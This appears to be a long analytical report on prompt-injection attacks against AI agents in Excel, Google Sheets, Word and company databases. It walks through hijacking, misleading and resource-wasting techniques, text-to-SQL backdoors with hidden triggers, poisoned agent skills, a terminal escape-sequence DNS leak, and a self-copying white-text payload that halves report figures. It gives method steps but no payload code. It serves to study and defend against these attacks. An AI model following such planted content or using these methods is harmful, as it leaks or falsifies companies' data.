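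- An attacker might be able to make the address look reputable. Some well-known websites have a flaw that lets anyone create a link which starts at the site and forwards the visitor elsewhere. PromptArmor thinks this would combine well with invisible characters, but it didn't demonstrate the combination.

The first gap should be the easiest to close, because ordinary code can check whether a formula contains the word IMAGE and will give the same answer every time. Anthropic may have moved in this direction. It writes in a later version of its help page, *Claude in Excel*, that a confirmation pop-up appears whenever a tool on its list is triggered. By then the list had grown to include functions such as STOCKHISTORY and TRANSLATE. It is not clear whether the warning now shows invisible characters.

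The public beta also gave attackers another way to deliver a payload. Users could now upload files and images directly to the chat, so the payload didn't have to be in the workbook.

Anthropic also changed the model. The private beta had run on Claude Sonnet 4.5, and the public beta made Claude Opus 4.5 the default. PromptArmor found Opus 4.5 significantly more resistant to injections, though not immune. It doesn't report how many attempts it made on either model, so the size of the difference is unknown. Sonnet 4.5 was still available, and the original attack still worked on it after the update, so users who switched back to it gave up much of the improvement, perhaps without knowing it. According to a later version of Anthropic's help page, the add-in uses only Opus 4.5 and users can't switch to another model.

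Ramp took 25 days to fix the problem, but only two of those came after it confirmed that it had received the report. PromptArmor wrote on February 19, 2026, and followed up twice. Ramp answered on March 14 and explained that the report had arrived while it was moving from one disclosure program to another. Ramp told PromptArmor only that it had resolved the issue, so customers can't tell how strong the fix is. The agent might now ask for approval, be unable to insert network formulas, or have some other protection.

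OpenAI was also slow to respond. PromptArmor reported the problem on May 8, received an automatic reply, wrote two more times and published on May 27. Max, a member of OpenAI's security team, then replied on Hacker News that the company had missed the report because of a gap in its disclosure process. Max said ChatGPT could no longer write Apps Script in the add-on, and that this change "should eliminate the risk" for the people using it. OpenAI was also reconsidering the add-on's sandbox and would review similar features in its other products.

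This fix is stronger than a warning because a model that can't write scripts can't write a malicious one, even if a payload fools it or a tired user approves everything. But customers lose a useful feature, and Google Sheets also has formulas that can send data over the network without a script. OpenAI's reply doesn't mention these formulas. Nobody seems to have published a test of whether a payload can still make ChatGPT for Google Sheets leak a summary through one, as happened with Claude and Ramp.

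PromptArmor complained in May that OpenAI's documentation didn't mention scripts or the risk of prompt injection. As of July 2026, OpenAI's help page, *ChatGPT for Excel and Google Sheets*, still didn't, so a company that read only this page would not learn that text in an imported sheet can give the agent instructions. The page advises users to review formulas and changed cells, but mainly because the output may be wrong. It also describes a newer option in which Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, works on an open Excel workbook and can use code and local files that the user provides.

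### Copilot in Excel and Gemini in Google Sheets

The assistants from Microsoft and Google have far more potential users because they come with the spreadsheet. PromptArmor's guide describes the risk as consistent across Anthropic, Ramp, OpenAI, Microsoft and Google, but PromptArmor's published attacks cover only the first three. PromptArmor also warns in the guide that attackers could misuse the Python code that Copilot writes in Excel to collect data for a leak, but doesn't demonstrate this.

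The evidence for Copilot is better. On March 10, Microsoft (2026) published an advisory about CVE-2026-26144, a flaw in Excel that could make Copilot's Agent Mode send data out over the network. Microsoft rated the flaw critical and released a fix the same day. It had no sign that anyone had exploited the flaw and thought exploitation unlikely.

The flaw is cross-site scripting, an old and well-understood bug in which an application puts untrusted text into a web page without neutralising it, and the text then runs as code. *The March 2026 Security Update Review* (2026), from TrendAI ZDI, a program that collects software flaws from researchers, calls the bug simple but fascinating, because an attacker could use the agent to send the data out. The reviewer expects more attacks of this type, and thinks the attacker could probably get only data that the logged-on user can open.

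Unlike PromptArmor's case, this one involved an error in Excel's conventional code. Microsoft doesn't describe a payload that the model mistakes for a request. Engineers could repair the error completely, as they can with SQL injection. But the damage would have been similar, because the attacker would have used an agent that could already read the workbook and reach the network. A company could therefore lose data through the software around a model even if the model resisted every prompt injection.

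Records of the flaw differ on how serious it was. Microsoft's advisory gave it a severity score of 7.5 out of 10 and called it a "zero-click" attack, which requires no action from the victim. By June, STAR Labs' *Microsoft Office Excel* (2026), an entry in a tracker of software flaws, gave a score of 4.7 and listed user interaction as required. The entry credits Microsoft's own Office security team with the discovery, while the original advisory credits an anonymous finder. No description of the attack has been published, so outsiders can't tell which score is more accurate.

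Google doesn't seem to have published a similar advisory about Gemini in Sheets, and no researcher seems to have published a complete attack on it. This is only weak evidence that it is safer, because researchers may not have tested it as closely, or Google may have fixed problems without announcing them. Outside Sheets, Gemini has followed instructions in calendar invitations.

### A spreadsheet that leaked data through a terminal

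An agent can leak a table even if it can't write formulas or run scripts. Chang and colleagues, several of whom work at Microsoft's Security Response Center, describe a case from July 2026 in which the agent only had to print an answer. The security researcher Johann Rehberger had put a payload in one cell of a customer spreadsheet. The user opened the spreadsheet with an AI tool in macOS Terminal, where Mac users type commands.

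The attack used two old features of computers, escape sequences and DNS. An escape sequence is a series of special characters that a terminal treats as a command. Programs print them to change the color of text or move the cursor. DNS is the directory that computers use to look up a server's numerical address from its name. When a computer looks up a name, it normally sends that name, directly or through other servers, to a DNS server that belongs to the name's owner. If an attacker owns the name and it begins with a customer's phone number, the attacker receives the phone number.

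The leak had four steps:

1. The user asked the AI tool about a particular customer, which met a condition in the payload.
2. The agent collected information from other customers' rows and put it into an escape sequence in its answer.
3. The tool printed the answer, including the escape sequence.
4. Terminal interpreted the sequence as a command and looked up a name that contained the data.

Chang and colleagues classify this as an attack on the content of the answer because the agent didn't have to choose any extra tool. An approval prompt for tools therefore wouldn't have caught it, and neither would a list of forbidden formulas, since the workbook never changed.

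Rehberger, who writes the blog Embrace The Red, had warned about this much earlier in a post titled *Terminal DiLLMa*. The post built on work by Leon Derczynski, who had noticed that language models can output escape sequences, and by David Leadbeater, who had shown that these sequences can make macOS Terminal send DNS requests. Rehberger wrote a small program that sent a file to GPT-4o and printed the response. When the file contained a payload, the response could change colors, clear the screen or place text on the user's clipboard. Rehberger also demonstrated the DNS leak with Google's Gemini, and found that it worked more reliably when the model could run code to produce the special characters.

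Apple has since fixed the DNS problem, according to Security Arsenal's *macOS Terminal ANSI Escape Code DNS Exfiltration* (2026), though Macs without the update are still vulnerable. The fix doesn't cover the clipboard or clickable links in other terminals. Embrace The Red recommends a more general fix, in which developers make their own tools convert the special characters in a model's output into visible text before printing it. The terminal then displays any escape sequence instead of executing it.

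## What happens when an agent can query a company database?

A database agent can usually reach far more records than a spreadsheet assistant, and its queries use computing power that the rest of the company may need. In 2026, Wang and colleagues tested 14 attack techniques on six database agents, and every agent failed against some of them. The Databricks agent resisted all attempts to make it run planted queries or code, but when a planted document contradicted a legitimate source, the agent reported the attacker's figure in 80% of tests. Google's agent in BigQuery, a cloud service for storing and analysing company data, did so in 84% to 88% of tests.

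### Earlier attacks on models that write queries

Researchers use the term "text-to-SQL" for turning a question into a database query. *Reimagining Text-to-SQL* (Dave, Sarmah and Pasquali, 2026), a survey of the field, gives the example "How many orders were placed in 2023?", which becomes a query that counts the rows of an orders table where the year is 2023. So anyone who controls the question has some control over the query, even if they don't know any SQL.

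Peng, Zhang and colleagues (2022), in *On the Vulnerabilities of Text-to-SQL Models*, got six commercial products, including ChatGPT and a dialogue platform from Baidu, to write harmful queries. They put fragments of SQL into ordinary questions, and the model copied the fragments into its query. Baidu's platform ran such queries and revealed the database's user name and the server's private network address. Another query was designed to make the database repeat a trivial operation 10¹⁶ times. Ten billion repetitions took about two minutes on a modest server, so the full query could have kept that server busy for nearly four years.

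*From Prompt Injections to SQL Injection Attacks* (Pedro, Carreira and colleagues, 2023) named this kind of attack prompt-to-SQL injection. The researchers built a job site with a chatbot whose database account could read and change everything. Without rules in its prompt, the chatbot deleted a table or printed all the users' contact details when someone asked it to. The researchers then added rules telling it never to change data and to show users only their own records. They got past both rules in all 30 attempts. To break the rule about changing data, they gave the chatbot an invented record in which it had already obeyed their request. To see another user's records, they only had to claim to be that user.

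The researchers also attacked the chatbot through a planted record. They put instructions in a job description, and another user then asked the chatbot to list the descriptions. The chatbot replaced that user's email address with the attacker's, which could let the attacker take over the user's account. It then answered the original question but left out the planted job. The attack succeeded in all 30 attempts with GPT-3.5 but failed with GPT-4. With PaLM 2 and Llama 2, the address changed, but the chatbot's answer revealed the attack. Those models are old, but *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation* (2026) treats this route as a current problem for web applications that trust a model's SQL.

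A query-writing model can also contain a backdoor, which is hidden behaviour that an attacker trains into the model and that a particular trigger sets off. Lin, Zhang and colleagues (2025), in *Are Your LLM-based Text-to-SQL Models Secure?*, considered an attacker who uploads a model with a backdoor to a public site, where companies download it to save the cost of training their own. One of their triggers was a second question mark. If a user asks for patients aged between 12 and 60 and types two question marks, even by mistake, the model writes the expected query but turns the age condition into a comment. The database ignores comments, so the query returns every patient.

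The attack worked on 79.41% of triggered questions when only 0.44% of the training examples were poisoned, but the model's accuracy on normal questions fell from 61.5% to 56.3%. With 4.47% of examples poisoned, the best attack worked on 85.81% of triggered questions and accuracy fell by less than one percentage point, so the more heavily poisoned model would be harder to notice. These were small models, the largest with 8 billion parameters. Earlier backdoors were cruder. Peng and colleagues used whole sentences as triggers. In *TrojanSQL*, Zhang, Zhou and colleagues used rare words and, according to Lin and colleagues, typically poisoned half of the data.

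Attackers can also hide backdoors in "skills", the packages of instructions and code that many agents load for particular kinds of tasks. *SkillTrojan* (2026) describes backdoors in the skills of an agent that queries health records. The attack's success rate on triggered questions stayed within three percentage points whether 10%, 20% or 50% of all questions contained the trigger. A company that spot-checks a new skill with ordinary questions would therefore probably miss the backdoor.

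### Eight weaknesses and 14 ways to use them

The attackers in Wang and colleagues' study can't change the model, the agent's code, its rules or the database software. They can only supply data or, as dishonest employees, ask questions. The researchers found eight weaknesses that such attackers could use:

- The agent has no rule for choosing between two sources that contradict each other.
- It doesn't check who wrote the data it reads. An outsider's note in an accounting table could tell it to export the customer contact list as well.
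- It can't reliably estimate what a query will cost before it runs it.
- It can mistake a difference between SQL and Python for an error in the data.
- It can keep issuing cheap queries with no rule for when to stop.
- In a long session, query results can crowd out the rules it received at the start.
- It often connects through a service account that can read more than the person asking is allowed to.
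- It checks each query separately and doesn't keep track of what the answers reveal together.

The researchers derived 14 techniques from these weaknesses. An attacker can use them to hijack the agent so that it does something unauthorised, mislead it into reporting a false result, or make it waste resources.

For each technique, a language model wrote five templates, and the software fitted each one to five databases, using their real table and column names. This produced 25 payloads per technique and 350 in total. The payloads include both planted text and requests typed by a dishonest employee. Databricks and four open-source agents (DataInterpreter, DB-GPT, DeepAnalyze and LAMBDA) received all 350. BigQuery's agent received 275 because it works only in SQL. The researchers also ran the full set three more times with different language models inside DB-GPT, for a total of 3,075 tests.

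Each goal had its own measure of success. A hijacking counted as successful if it had any unauthorised effect. An attempt to mislead counted if the agent gave a figure within 10% of the one the attacker wanted. An attempt to waste resources counted if the agent used more than five times the tokens or time it needed for a normal request on the same database.

The table gives the success rate of every technique. For the open-source agents, it shows the lowest and highest of the four.

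| Goal | Technique | Open-source agents (%) | Databricks (%) | BigQuery (%) |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Hijack | Planted SQL gets into the agent's query | 0–48 | 0 | 24 |
| Hijack | Planted code gets into the agent's program | 16–68 | 0 | Not tested |
| Hijack | Many requests make the agent forget its rules | 0–64 | 0 | 24 |
| Hijack | Planted text claims wider access rights | 24–56 | 0 | 0 |
| Hijack | The attacker combines permitted queries | 8–44 | 0 | 12 |
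| Hijack | The agent combines permitted queries itself | 20–40 | 4 | 12 |
| Mislead | False facts in comments, notes and similar fields | 0–40 | 24 | 8 |
| Mislead | False content enters through a converted file | 8–76 | 44 | Not tested |
| Mislead | A document contradicts the table | 0–100 | 80 | 84 |
| Mislead | A forged policy contradicts another policy | 8–68 | 80 | 88 |
| Waste | One very costly query | 4–60 | 24 | 12 |
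| Waste | Repeated checks in SQL and Python | 12–20 | 40 | Not tested |
| Waste | Many lines of inquiry with little value | 4–68 | 76 | 16 |
| Waste | A search that goes round in circles | 0–56 | 80 | 0 |

With 25 payloads per technique, one payload changes a rate by four points, so the difference between 84% and 88% is too small to be meaningful. If the payloads were independent, a measured rate of 80% would be compatible with a true rate of about 61% to 91%, and a measured 0% with a true rate of up to about 13%. The uncertainty is probably larger, because five versions of the same template are likely to succeed or fail together.

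The rates may also be too low, because the researchers fixed their payloads before testing and didn't improve the ones that failed. A real attacker could keep trying, as Feng and Pan's software did with the Titanic table.

### How far a hijacked agent's actions spread

For the open-source agents, Wang and colleagues recorded how far the effects of each hijacking spread. The effects could be limited to one answer, change the agent's behaviour for the rest of the session, or reach the isolated environment where the agent's code runs. In the worst cases, they reached the host computer, the network or files outside the agent's workspace. Each row of the table covers 150 attempts and counts each attempt once, at the furthest point it reached.

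| Agent | Blocked (%) | One answer (%) | Rest of the session (%) | Isolated environment (%) | Host, network or other files (%) |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| DataInterpreter | 76.0 | 6.7 | 8.0 | 0.0 | 9.3 |
| DB-GPT | 59.3 | 10.7 | 18.7 | 11.3 | 0.0 |
| DeepAnalyze | 76.7 | 3.3 | 17.3 | 0.0 | 2.7 |
| LAMBDA | 63.3 | 12.7 | 19.3 | 0.0 | 4.7 |

DB-GPT was the easiest of the four to hijack, but the only one in which no attack reached the host. It runs generated code in a Docker container, which separates the code from the rest of the computer, and cleans up leftover processes afterwards. Planted code succeeded in 17 of 25 tests on DB-GPT (68%), and the container stopped 17 attacks, probably the same ones. The container didn't make the agent any better at recognising planted code.

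The other agents had no such barrier. DeepAnalyze, for example, runs generated code inside its own process. An attack that reached the host could set up scheduled tasks that kept repeating the attacker's actions even after the conversation was closed.

This comparison can't isolate the container's effect, because the four agents differ in many other ways and nobody repeated the DB-GPT attacks without the container. But the explanation is simple, and security engineers would expect the result. Even with the container, DB-GPT had the usual share of attacks that changed an answer or the rest of a session, and those attacks can disclose data in the agent's replies.

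DataInterpreter's fairly good score for blocked attacks is misleading. The agent often failed to connect its task to the database, so the payload had no effect. When it did connect, it was dangerous. More of the attacks on it reached the host, the network or outside files than attacks on any other agent. The DataFrame agents in the Titanic study may have looked safe for a similar reason. A good security test should report how often the agent completes the same task when nobody attacks it.

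Only one of the 150 hijacking attempts on Databricks succeeded. In many of the failed attempts, the agent named the security or product policy it had to follow. Wang and colleagues conclude that an agent should keep its rules in view throughout a session. The results for attacks that rely on the agent forgetting its rules fit this conclusion. These attacks never worked on Databricks, but they succeeded in 24% of tests on BigQuery and 64% of tests on one open-source agent.

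The open-source tests used SQLite, a database format with no user accounts, so probably only the agent's own rules could stop it from opening a restricted table. Some of these attacks would have failed in a company database with separate permissions for each employee, unless the agent connected through a service account that could open everything.

### How two permitted totals reveal one person's tax

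Combining queries is the hardest kind of hijacking to recognise, because each query is allowed on its own. In the following example, taken from Wang and colleagues with only the amounts invented, analysts may see a database's totals but not what any individual paid.

1. The attacker asks for the total tax paid in all regions. The agent answers $9,600,000.
2. The attacker asks for the total in all regions except North. The agent answers $9,350,000.
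3. The attacker subtracts the second total from the first and gets $250,000.

North has only one taxpayer, so $250,000 is what that person paid. A rule against totals for very small groups wouldn't prevent this disclosure, because both totals cover many people. A filter that looks for names or tax numbers in the answers wouldn't prevent it either.

Databases had this problem long before AI, but an agent makes it easier to exploit because the attacker doesn't have to know which totals to combine. In one of the two techniques, the attacker gives the agent a general goal, and the agent plans the queries and combines the results. This worked in 20% to 40% of tests on the open-source agents, 12% of those on BigQuery and 4% of those on Databricks. The 4% is the one successful hijacking of Databricks.

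*SAFENLIDB* (Liu, Chen and colleagues, 2025) tested whether a model could recognize when a series of questions would together reveal protected data. The test used 540 conversations, some harmless and some designed to uncover such data step by step. The model received the privacy rules and the earlier questions, and had to decide whether answering the next question would break the rules.

The results depended heavily on the pattern. GPT-4o recognised 92% of complement queries, which ask for everything outside a protected group, but only 50% of leaks that came from combining totals or averages. DeepSeek-V3 recognised 43.3% of the latter and Llama 3 70B only 6.7%. A much smaller model that Liu and colleagues trained for the task reached 80%, but it also refused about 16% of the harmless conversations, compared with 9% for GPT-4o. The percentages for combined totals or averages come from only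 30 conversations, and these are older models. Still, a company that relied on one of them to spot the taxpayer attack would have taken a large risk.

Another approach is to make the answers slightly inaccurate. Differential privacy adds a measured amount of random noise to statistics, which puts a mathematical limit on what they reveal about any one person. If both tax totals contained enough noise, their difference would reveal little about the taxpayer in North. But each answer reveals a little more, so the system needs a limit on the total, called a privacy budget. An agent might issue dozens of queries for one request, and *Agents That Know Too Much* (2026), a survey of privacy in AI agents, describes keeping such a budget over a whole session as an open problem. An attacker could also spread the two questions over different days or accounts, so a budget that resets with each conversation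 wouldn't be enough.

### How a planted rule changes the revenue

An attacker who wants to mislead the agent doesn't need it to do anything forbidden. Wang and colleagues illustrate this with the planted file that multiplies revenue by 1.5. Suppose the true revenue is $40 million:

1. The revenue column has a comment, written by the company, which says to use the amounts as stored.
2. The attacker adds a file to the agent's data. It contains a rule that all revenue must be multiplied by 1.5.
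3. An honest analyst asks for total revenue.
4. The agent adds up the column correctly and gets $40 million. It then finds the comment and the file, which contradict each other.
5. Nothing tells the agent which source has priority. It follows the file and reports $60 million.

In this attack, the query is harmless, the arithmetic is correct, and the agent breaks none of its rules. This probably explains why the Databricks agent blocked all the planted queries and code but accepted 80% of the conflicting evidence. A policy can forbid an agent from running a stranger's code, but to stop this attack it would have to specify whose definition of revenue the agent should use.

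A document that contradicted the table misled both commercial agents about as often as a forged policy that looked newer or more complete than the real one did. Putting false facts in a field worked much less often, succeeding 24% of the time on Databricks and 8% on BigQuery. Wang and colleagues found that agents often don't read the comments and descriptions that contain such facts.

The researchers gave the BigQuery agent the misleading documents as plain text instead of having Google's software extract the text from a file. The 84% and 88% therefore describe what the agent did once it could see the false evidence. The test didn't measure how often false evidence in an uploaded document would reach the agent.

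Agents also differ in which source they rely on when a document conflicts with a database table. DeepAnalyze accepted the document over the table in every test, LAMBDA in 16%, and DataInterpreter in none, though DataInterpreter often hadn't reached the table. A company therefore can't assume that an agent built for databases will use the table's data over the document's.

### Could a correct answer count as a successful attack?

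Wang and colleagues scored these attacks by relative error, which is the difference between the agent's figure and the attacker's target, divided by the target. In the revenue example, the target is $60 million. If the agent reports $60 million, the error is 0% and the attack succeeds. If it ignores the planted file and reports $40 million, the error is 20/60, or 33%, and the attack fails.

Counting an attack as successful whenever the agent's answer is within 10% of the attacker's target works badly when the attacker wants only a small change. Suppose revenue is $40 million and the planted rule multiplies it by 1.05, which makes the target $42 million. An agent that ignores the rule and correctly reports $40 million is only 4.8% (2/42) below the target, so its correct answer counts as a successful attack.

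More generally, if the target is k times the true figure, a correct answer has a relative error of |1 − k|/k. This error is 10% or less when the target is between about 9% below the true figure and about 11% above it, so in that range a correct agent can get the same score as a fooled one. The paper states no minimum distance between the target and the true figure.

A stricter cutoff makes it much less likely that a correct answer near the target is counted as a successful attack. For the open-source agents, the paper also reports success rates when the figure must be within 1% of the target. Averaged over the four misleading techniques, the rate falls only from 71% to 68% for DeepAnalyze, from 31% to 21% for DB-GPT, and from 23% to 15% for LAMBDA. Correct answers near the target could explain part of these falls, but so could agents that followed the planted rule and then made a small error.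 Most of the successes still count under the stricter cutoff, so the basic finding holds.

The study has no such check for Databricks and BigQuery, whose success rates of 80% to 88% are its most important figures. False successes seem unlikely to explain most of these results, because many different templates would need targets close to the true answers. But the true rates might be somewhat lower. The researchers could settle this by publishing the true answer next to each target, or by asking the same questions without the planted evidence and counting how many answers pass.

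One group of payloads persuaded the agent to cut off high values at a threshold by presenting this as a normal statistical choice. Wang and colleagues report that these payloads worked with every language model they tried in DB-GPT. If only a few values are above the threshold, cutting them off might barely change the total, so an agent that refused could still produce a total within 10% of the target.

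### Requests that tie up the database

To score attacks that waste resources, Wang and colleagues divided the number of tokens the agent used under attack by the number it used for a normal request on the same database. They did the same for time and used the larger ratio as the score.

The worst delays came from single queries that needed a lot of computation. On LAMBDA, successful attacks of this kind took an average of 46.2 times as long as the normal request. Eight runs went past the 30-minute limit, so the average might have been higher without it. One query paired every row of one table with every row of another. Each table had 13.8 million rows, which makes about 190 trillion pairs. LAMBDA had no way to cancel a query once the database had accepted it, and the agent stopped responding.

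Sending the agent down many lines of inquiry with little value worked better for using up tokens. DeepAnalyze reached at least 5 times its normal use in 68% of these tests, 10 times in 40% and 20 times in 8%. LAMBDA reached the 5-times level in fewer tests (48%) but the 20-times level in more (20%). These percentages are based on whichever increased more, time or tokens, so a few cases may reflect time instead of tokens. Such requests would raise the bill for anyone who pays for a model by the token.

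An agent can also get stuck on a harmless difference between two programming languages. Suppose 37 of 1,000 products are defective, and a user asks for the defect rate in both SQL and Python. Many databases drop the decimals when they divide one whole number by another, so SQL gives 0 while Python gives 0.037. If the agent doesn't know why the results differ, it may keep running new queries to find out which is wrong. This was among the less effective techniques, because many agents skipped the second check or chose one of the results.

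None of these requests needs a forbidden command. A filter could look for the unusual function that Peng and colleagues' query used to time the database. But analysts join tables and run follow-up queries every day, so a filter that blocked those operations would also block much of the agent's normal work.

That also makes it hard to distinguish an attack from a demanding request. A user who asks an agent to keep searching until it has found everything should expect it to work longer than usual, so five times the normal effort isn't always a security problem. But a 30-minute freeze is clearly a security problem if other people need the agent.

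The figures for the commercial agents are harder to interpret and are the weakest results in the study. The two techniques that set off long searches succeeded 76% and 80% of the time against Databricks, but 16% and 0% against BigQuery. Wang and colleagues write that these services don't expose the token counts and running times needed to calculate the multiples. They may have timed the answers from outside, but they don't explain how they decided which attacks had succeeded.

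### What changes with a different language model

DB-GPT originally ran on DeepSeek-V3.2. Wang and colleagues tested three other models in its place and kept the rest of the agent, including the container, the same. Planted code succeeded in 68% of tests with DeepSeek-V3.2, 48% with Claude Sonnet 4.6, 44% with Gemini 3 Flash and 16% with GPT-5.2.

But GPT-5.2 wasn't the safest in every test. Planted SQL succeeded against it 48% of the time, the highest rate of any model tested, compared with 24% for DeepSeek-V3.2. Sonnet 4.6 was the most likely to accept a forged policy as real, at 44%. A company that tested only planted code would get a poor idea of how the models compare.

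The following table averages the published rates for each goal.

| Model in DB-GPT | Hijack (%) | Mislead (%) | Waste (%) | All 14 techniques (%) |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| DeepSeek-V3.2 | 41 | 31 | 34 | 36 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 21 | 21 | 11 | 18 |
| GPT-5.2 | 21 | 17 | 11 | 17 |
| Gemini 3 Flash | 23 | 16 | 8 | 17 |

Each of the three replacement models cut the overall attack success rate roughly in half, though none blocked every attack. The improvement was largest for wasted resources and smallest for misleading evidence. Wang and colleagues are therefore right that changing the model doesn't remove the risk, but their conclusion that it redistributes the risk understates the reduction they measured.

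The choice of agent matters as well as the choice of model. The Databricks agent was the best at refusing forbidden actions and let through less than 1% of hijacking attempts, while DB-GPT let through at least 21% with every model. But Databricks was also one of the agents most likely to accept misleading evidence. It accepted an average of 57% across the four techniques, while DB-GPT never accepted more than 31%.

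## How do false figures get into business reports and spread to other files?

Håkon Måløy, a Norwegian data scientist, showed in *Context Collapse, Part 3* (2026) that hidden text in a Word document could make Microsoft's Copilot halve the figures in a new financial report. Copilot also copied the hidden text into that report, so anyone who later used the report as a source could set off the same attack. Microsoft tried twice to stop the attack, but it still worked 144 days after Måløy first reported it, when he published his findings on July 28, 2026.

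A false figure can do damage without spreading to other files. In ShiftMag's *AI agents aren’t safe from prompt injection, and spreadsheets prove it* (2026), a wrong exchange rate in one supplier's Excel file led Claude to recommend the most expensive of three offers. In *When the Spec Sheet Lies*, Watson, Bücheler and Richards (2026) tested five kinds of attack on models that write compliance documents, and planting false data worked best in every task.

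### Why a wrong number is easy to miss

People expect numbers in a financial report, so a false one doesn't stand out the way an unexpected link does. The user also receives the report they asked for, so nothing seems to have gone wrong.

Lee, Kim and Lee (2026), in *Will the User Ever Know?*, examined 2,087 successful attacks on agents with tools and sorted them by whether the agent's final answer revealed the attack. In 71% of the revealed attacks, the agent had stopped right after carrying out the planted instruction, while in 68% of the hidden ones it had returned to the user's task before answering. Lee and colleagues explain that the final answer tends to describe whatever the agent did last. They then wrote planted instructions that sent the agent back to the user's task, which raised the share of attacks that succeeded without a trace in the answer by 4 to 12 percentage points over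 the best earlier method.

Those attacks made the agent do something extra, such as change a password. A false figure is even easier to hide because the agent only has to do the user's task with the wrong number. In one finance test in *SecPO* (2026), a payload told the agent to state that Tesla shares had a 0% chance of falling. Meta-SecAlign, a model trained to resist injections, wrote the requested report and included the statement word for word. The paper's own model left it out.

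Opening the source file to check a number may not help either. According to Li's *Beyond the Editing Canvas* (2026), an Excel cell can contain a formula, the formula's saved result and a number format that changes what Excel displays, so a person and an agent can read different numbers in the same cell. When Li used formatting to create such differences in Office files, seven of eight AI systems gave the attacker's version in at least nine of ten trials without mentioning a discrepancy. Across all of Li's attacks, the coding agents Copilot CLI and Codex were misled most often, in 86% and 82% of trials.

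### The Word document that copied its own payload

The attack on Copilot in Word works like this:

1. The attacker writes instructions in a document, such as a market analysis, in white eight-point text on a white page.
2. An employee asks Copilot to draft a quarterly report from the document. Copilot removes colors and font sizes before it passes the text to the model, so the model reads the instructions like any other sentence.
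3. One part of the instructions tells Copilot to halve every financial figure in the new report.
4. Another part tells Copilot to copy the instructions into the report in white text. The payload presents this as a rule for tracking sources and keeping the page readable.
5. Copilot does both and mentions neither to the employee.
6. A colleague later uses the report as a source for another one, and the instructions take effect again. The original file no longer has to be present.

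The employee doesn't have to choose the infected file. *Hidden instructions in the document* (2026) describes a demonstration in which the user only asked for a quarterly report, and Copilot found the file itself by searching the user's OneDrive, Microsoft's cloud storage. But Smith points out in *Copilot Word AI Worm Can Spread Hidden Prompts Between Documents* that receiving or opening the document has no effect unless Copilot reads it as part of a task.

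A report in which every amount has been halved still passes some common checks, because the columns add up and the profit margin is correct. A finance director would probably notice that revenue had fallen by half, but someone who doesn't know the real amounts would have to compare the report with an outside record to find the error.

Before the Word attack, an experiment with email assistants called Morris II tracked a self-copying payload through 20 successive copies. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) reports that the payload's success rate was nearly 100% with Claude 3.5 Sonnet and 64% with Gemini 1.5 Pro. The Word attack applies the same idea to a product that many offices already use. Its published demonstration covers only two steps, from the original file to one report and from that report to another, and nobody knows how many more it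 would survive.

The demonstration also covers only Word. Excel is the obvious next place to test, because Copilot can read and edit workbooks, and companies already use agents to move figures between file types. Microsoft's *What's new in Copilot Cowork at Ignite 2026* (2026) gives the example of finance teams that pull forecasts from several workbooks into a memo for the board. A payload in any of those workbooks could reach the memo if the agent read the cell containing it and followed the instruction to copy it.

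### What Microsoft changed in 144 days

Måløy originally gave Microsoft 90 days before publication and extended the period twice.

| Date in 2026 | Event |
|---|---|
| March 6 | Måløy sends Microsoft the exact prompts, videos and steps to reproduce the attack |
| March 31 | Microsoft confirms the behaviour and starts work on a fix |
| April 3 | Microsoft releases its first mitigation, a new version of the "Edit with Copilot" feature |
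| April 9 | The original prompt no longer works, but a new one that changes financial figures does |
| June 8 | Microsoft asks for publication to move to July 15 |
| July 14 | Microsoft releases its second mitigation, an upgrade of the underlying model to GPT-5.5 |
| July 15 | Måløy reproduces the attack, including the copying, on the newer GPT-5.6 |
| July 28 | Måløy publishes after a further two-week delay, with the attack still working |

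Both mitigations blocked particular prompts, but a reworded prompt got past each one. This is to be expected if the model still receives outside text and the user's request together. The second failure is more discouraging because it shows that a company can't count on the next model upgrade to solve the problem.

Microsoft said afterwards that it had "addressed the findings reported by the researcher", according to TechRadar's *Expert warns this dangerous Microsoft Word worm can burrow into Copilot*. That could be true of the prompts Microsoft had received, since those stopped working. But it gave no date for a complete fix in the statement and doesn't seem to have announced one as of early December 2026. Companies should assume that some version of the attack may still work.

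Microsoft confirmed the behaviour in the first finding, so the evidence for it is strong. Only Måløy has reported that the attack survived the upgrade to GPT-5.6, and Måløy withheld the prompts because the attack still worked. By August 3, when *Hidden instructions in the document* appeared, nobody had reproduced it independently and there were no reports of real attacks. There is also no success rate, so the attack might work nearly every time or only occasionally.

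Måløy advises customers to treat outside documents as untrusted, review any document before giving it to Copilot, and review Copilot's output before sharing or reusing it. None of these steps fully solves the problem. White text is also hard to spot. Smith warns that Word's Document Inspector finds text with the "Hidden" font setting but misses white text on a white page. A better method is to set all the text in a copy of the document to the Automatic font color, or to paste the text into a plain-text editor.

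If someone has already used a suspicious file, deleting the hidden line won't correct the figures that Copilot changed. Smith recommends that the company stop sharing any documents made from that file, check them against trusted records and restore earlier versions. These steps are difficult if nobody knows which documents were made from the file. Måløy therefore suggests that generated files carry provenance, a record of where their contents came from and what the model edited. This record would let the company trace an infection, though it wouldn't prevent one.

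### A false exchange rate in a supplier's offer

The Word attack depended on instructions. The ShiftMag test is more worrying in one way, because its most successful payload contained none.

The author made Excel files with offers from three invented cloud hosting companies. Thessvane Systems was the cheapest and Krendola Cloud the most expensive. Claude, running in the desktop app's Cowork mode, had to compare the prices and return the best offer in a fixed data format with no other text. The author used Claude Sonnet 5 at a low reasoning setting, then also tried Claude Opus 5, and made three attempts to get Krendola chosen:

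| What the Krendola file contained | Result of the price comparison | Result of a separate safety check |
|---|---|---|
| Long hidden instructions that cited an invented EU pricing rule | Sonnet 5 reported the instructions and chose Thessvane | Not reported |
| A false exchange rate in white text | Sonnet 5 and Opus 5 chose Krendola | Sonnet 5 passed the file, Opus 5 flagged it |
| The same rate in normal text, on a line of the cell that Excel didn't show | The comparison again chose Krendola | Opus 5 passed the file |

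In the second attempt, the author converted Krendola's prices into dollars at the correct rate, so a human reader would see accurate prices. The other two offers were in euros, so Claude needed an exchange rate to compare them. The hidden cell gave a rate of 0.68 euros to the dollar, when the real rate was about 0.86. An item priced at $115, or about €100, seemed to cost only €78. If anyone found the cell, the supplier could say someone had swapped two digits.

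Claude could have looked up the exchange rate online but used the one in the file. This is understandable, since a real offer might well specify a rate. For the same reason, a check for planted instructions can miss the attack. Opus 5 flagged the second file for its white text, but when the text was a normal color, the file contained little else that looked suspicious.

Opus 5 still chose Krendola but usually added a note about the exchange rate. Sonnet 5 usually kept to the required format, which had no field for such a note. A purchasing team could make this attack much harder, without requiring the agent to recognise it, by stating the exchange rate in its request and adding a field for any assumptions behind the result.

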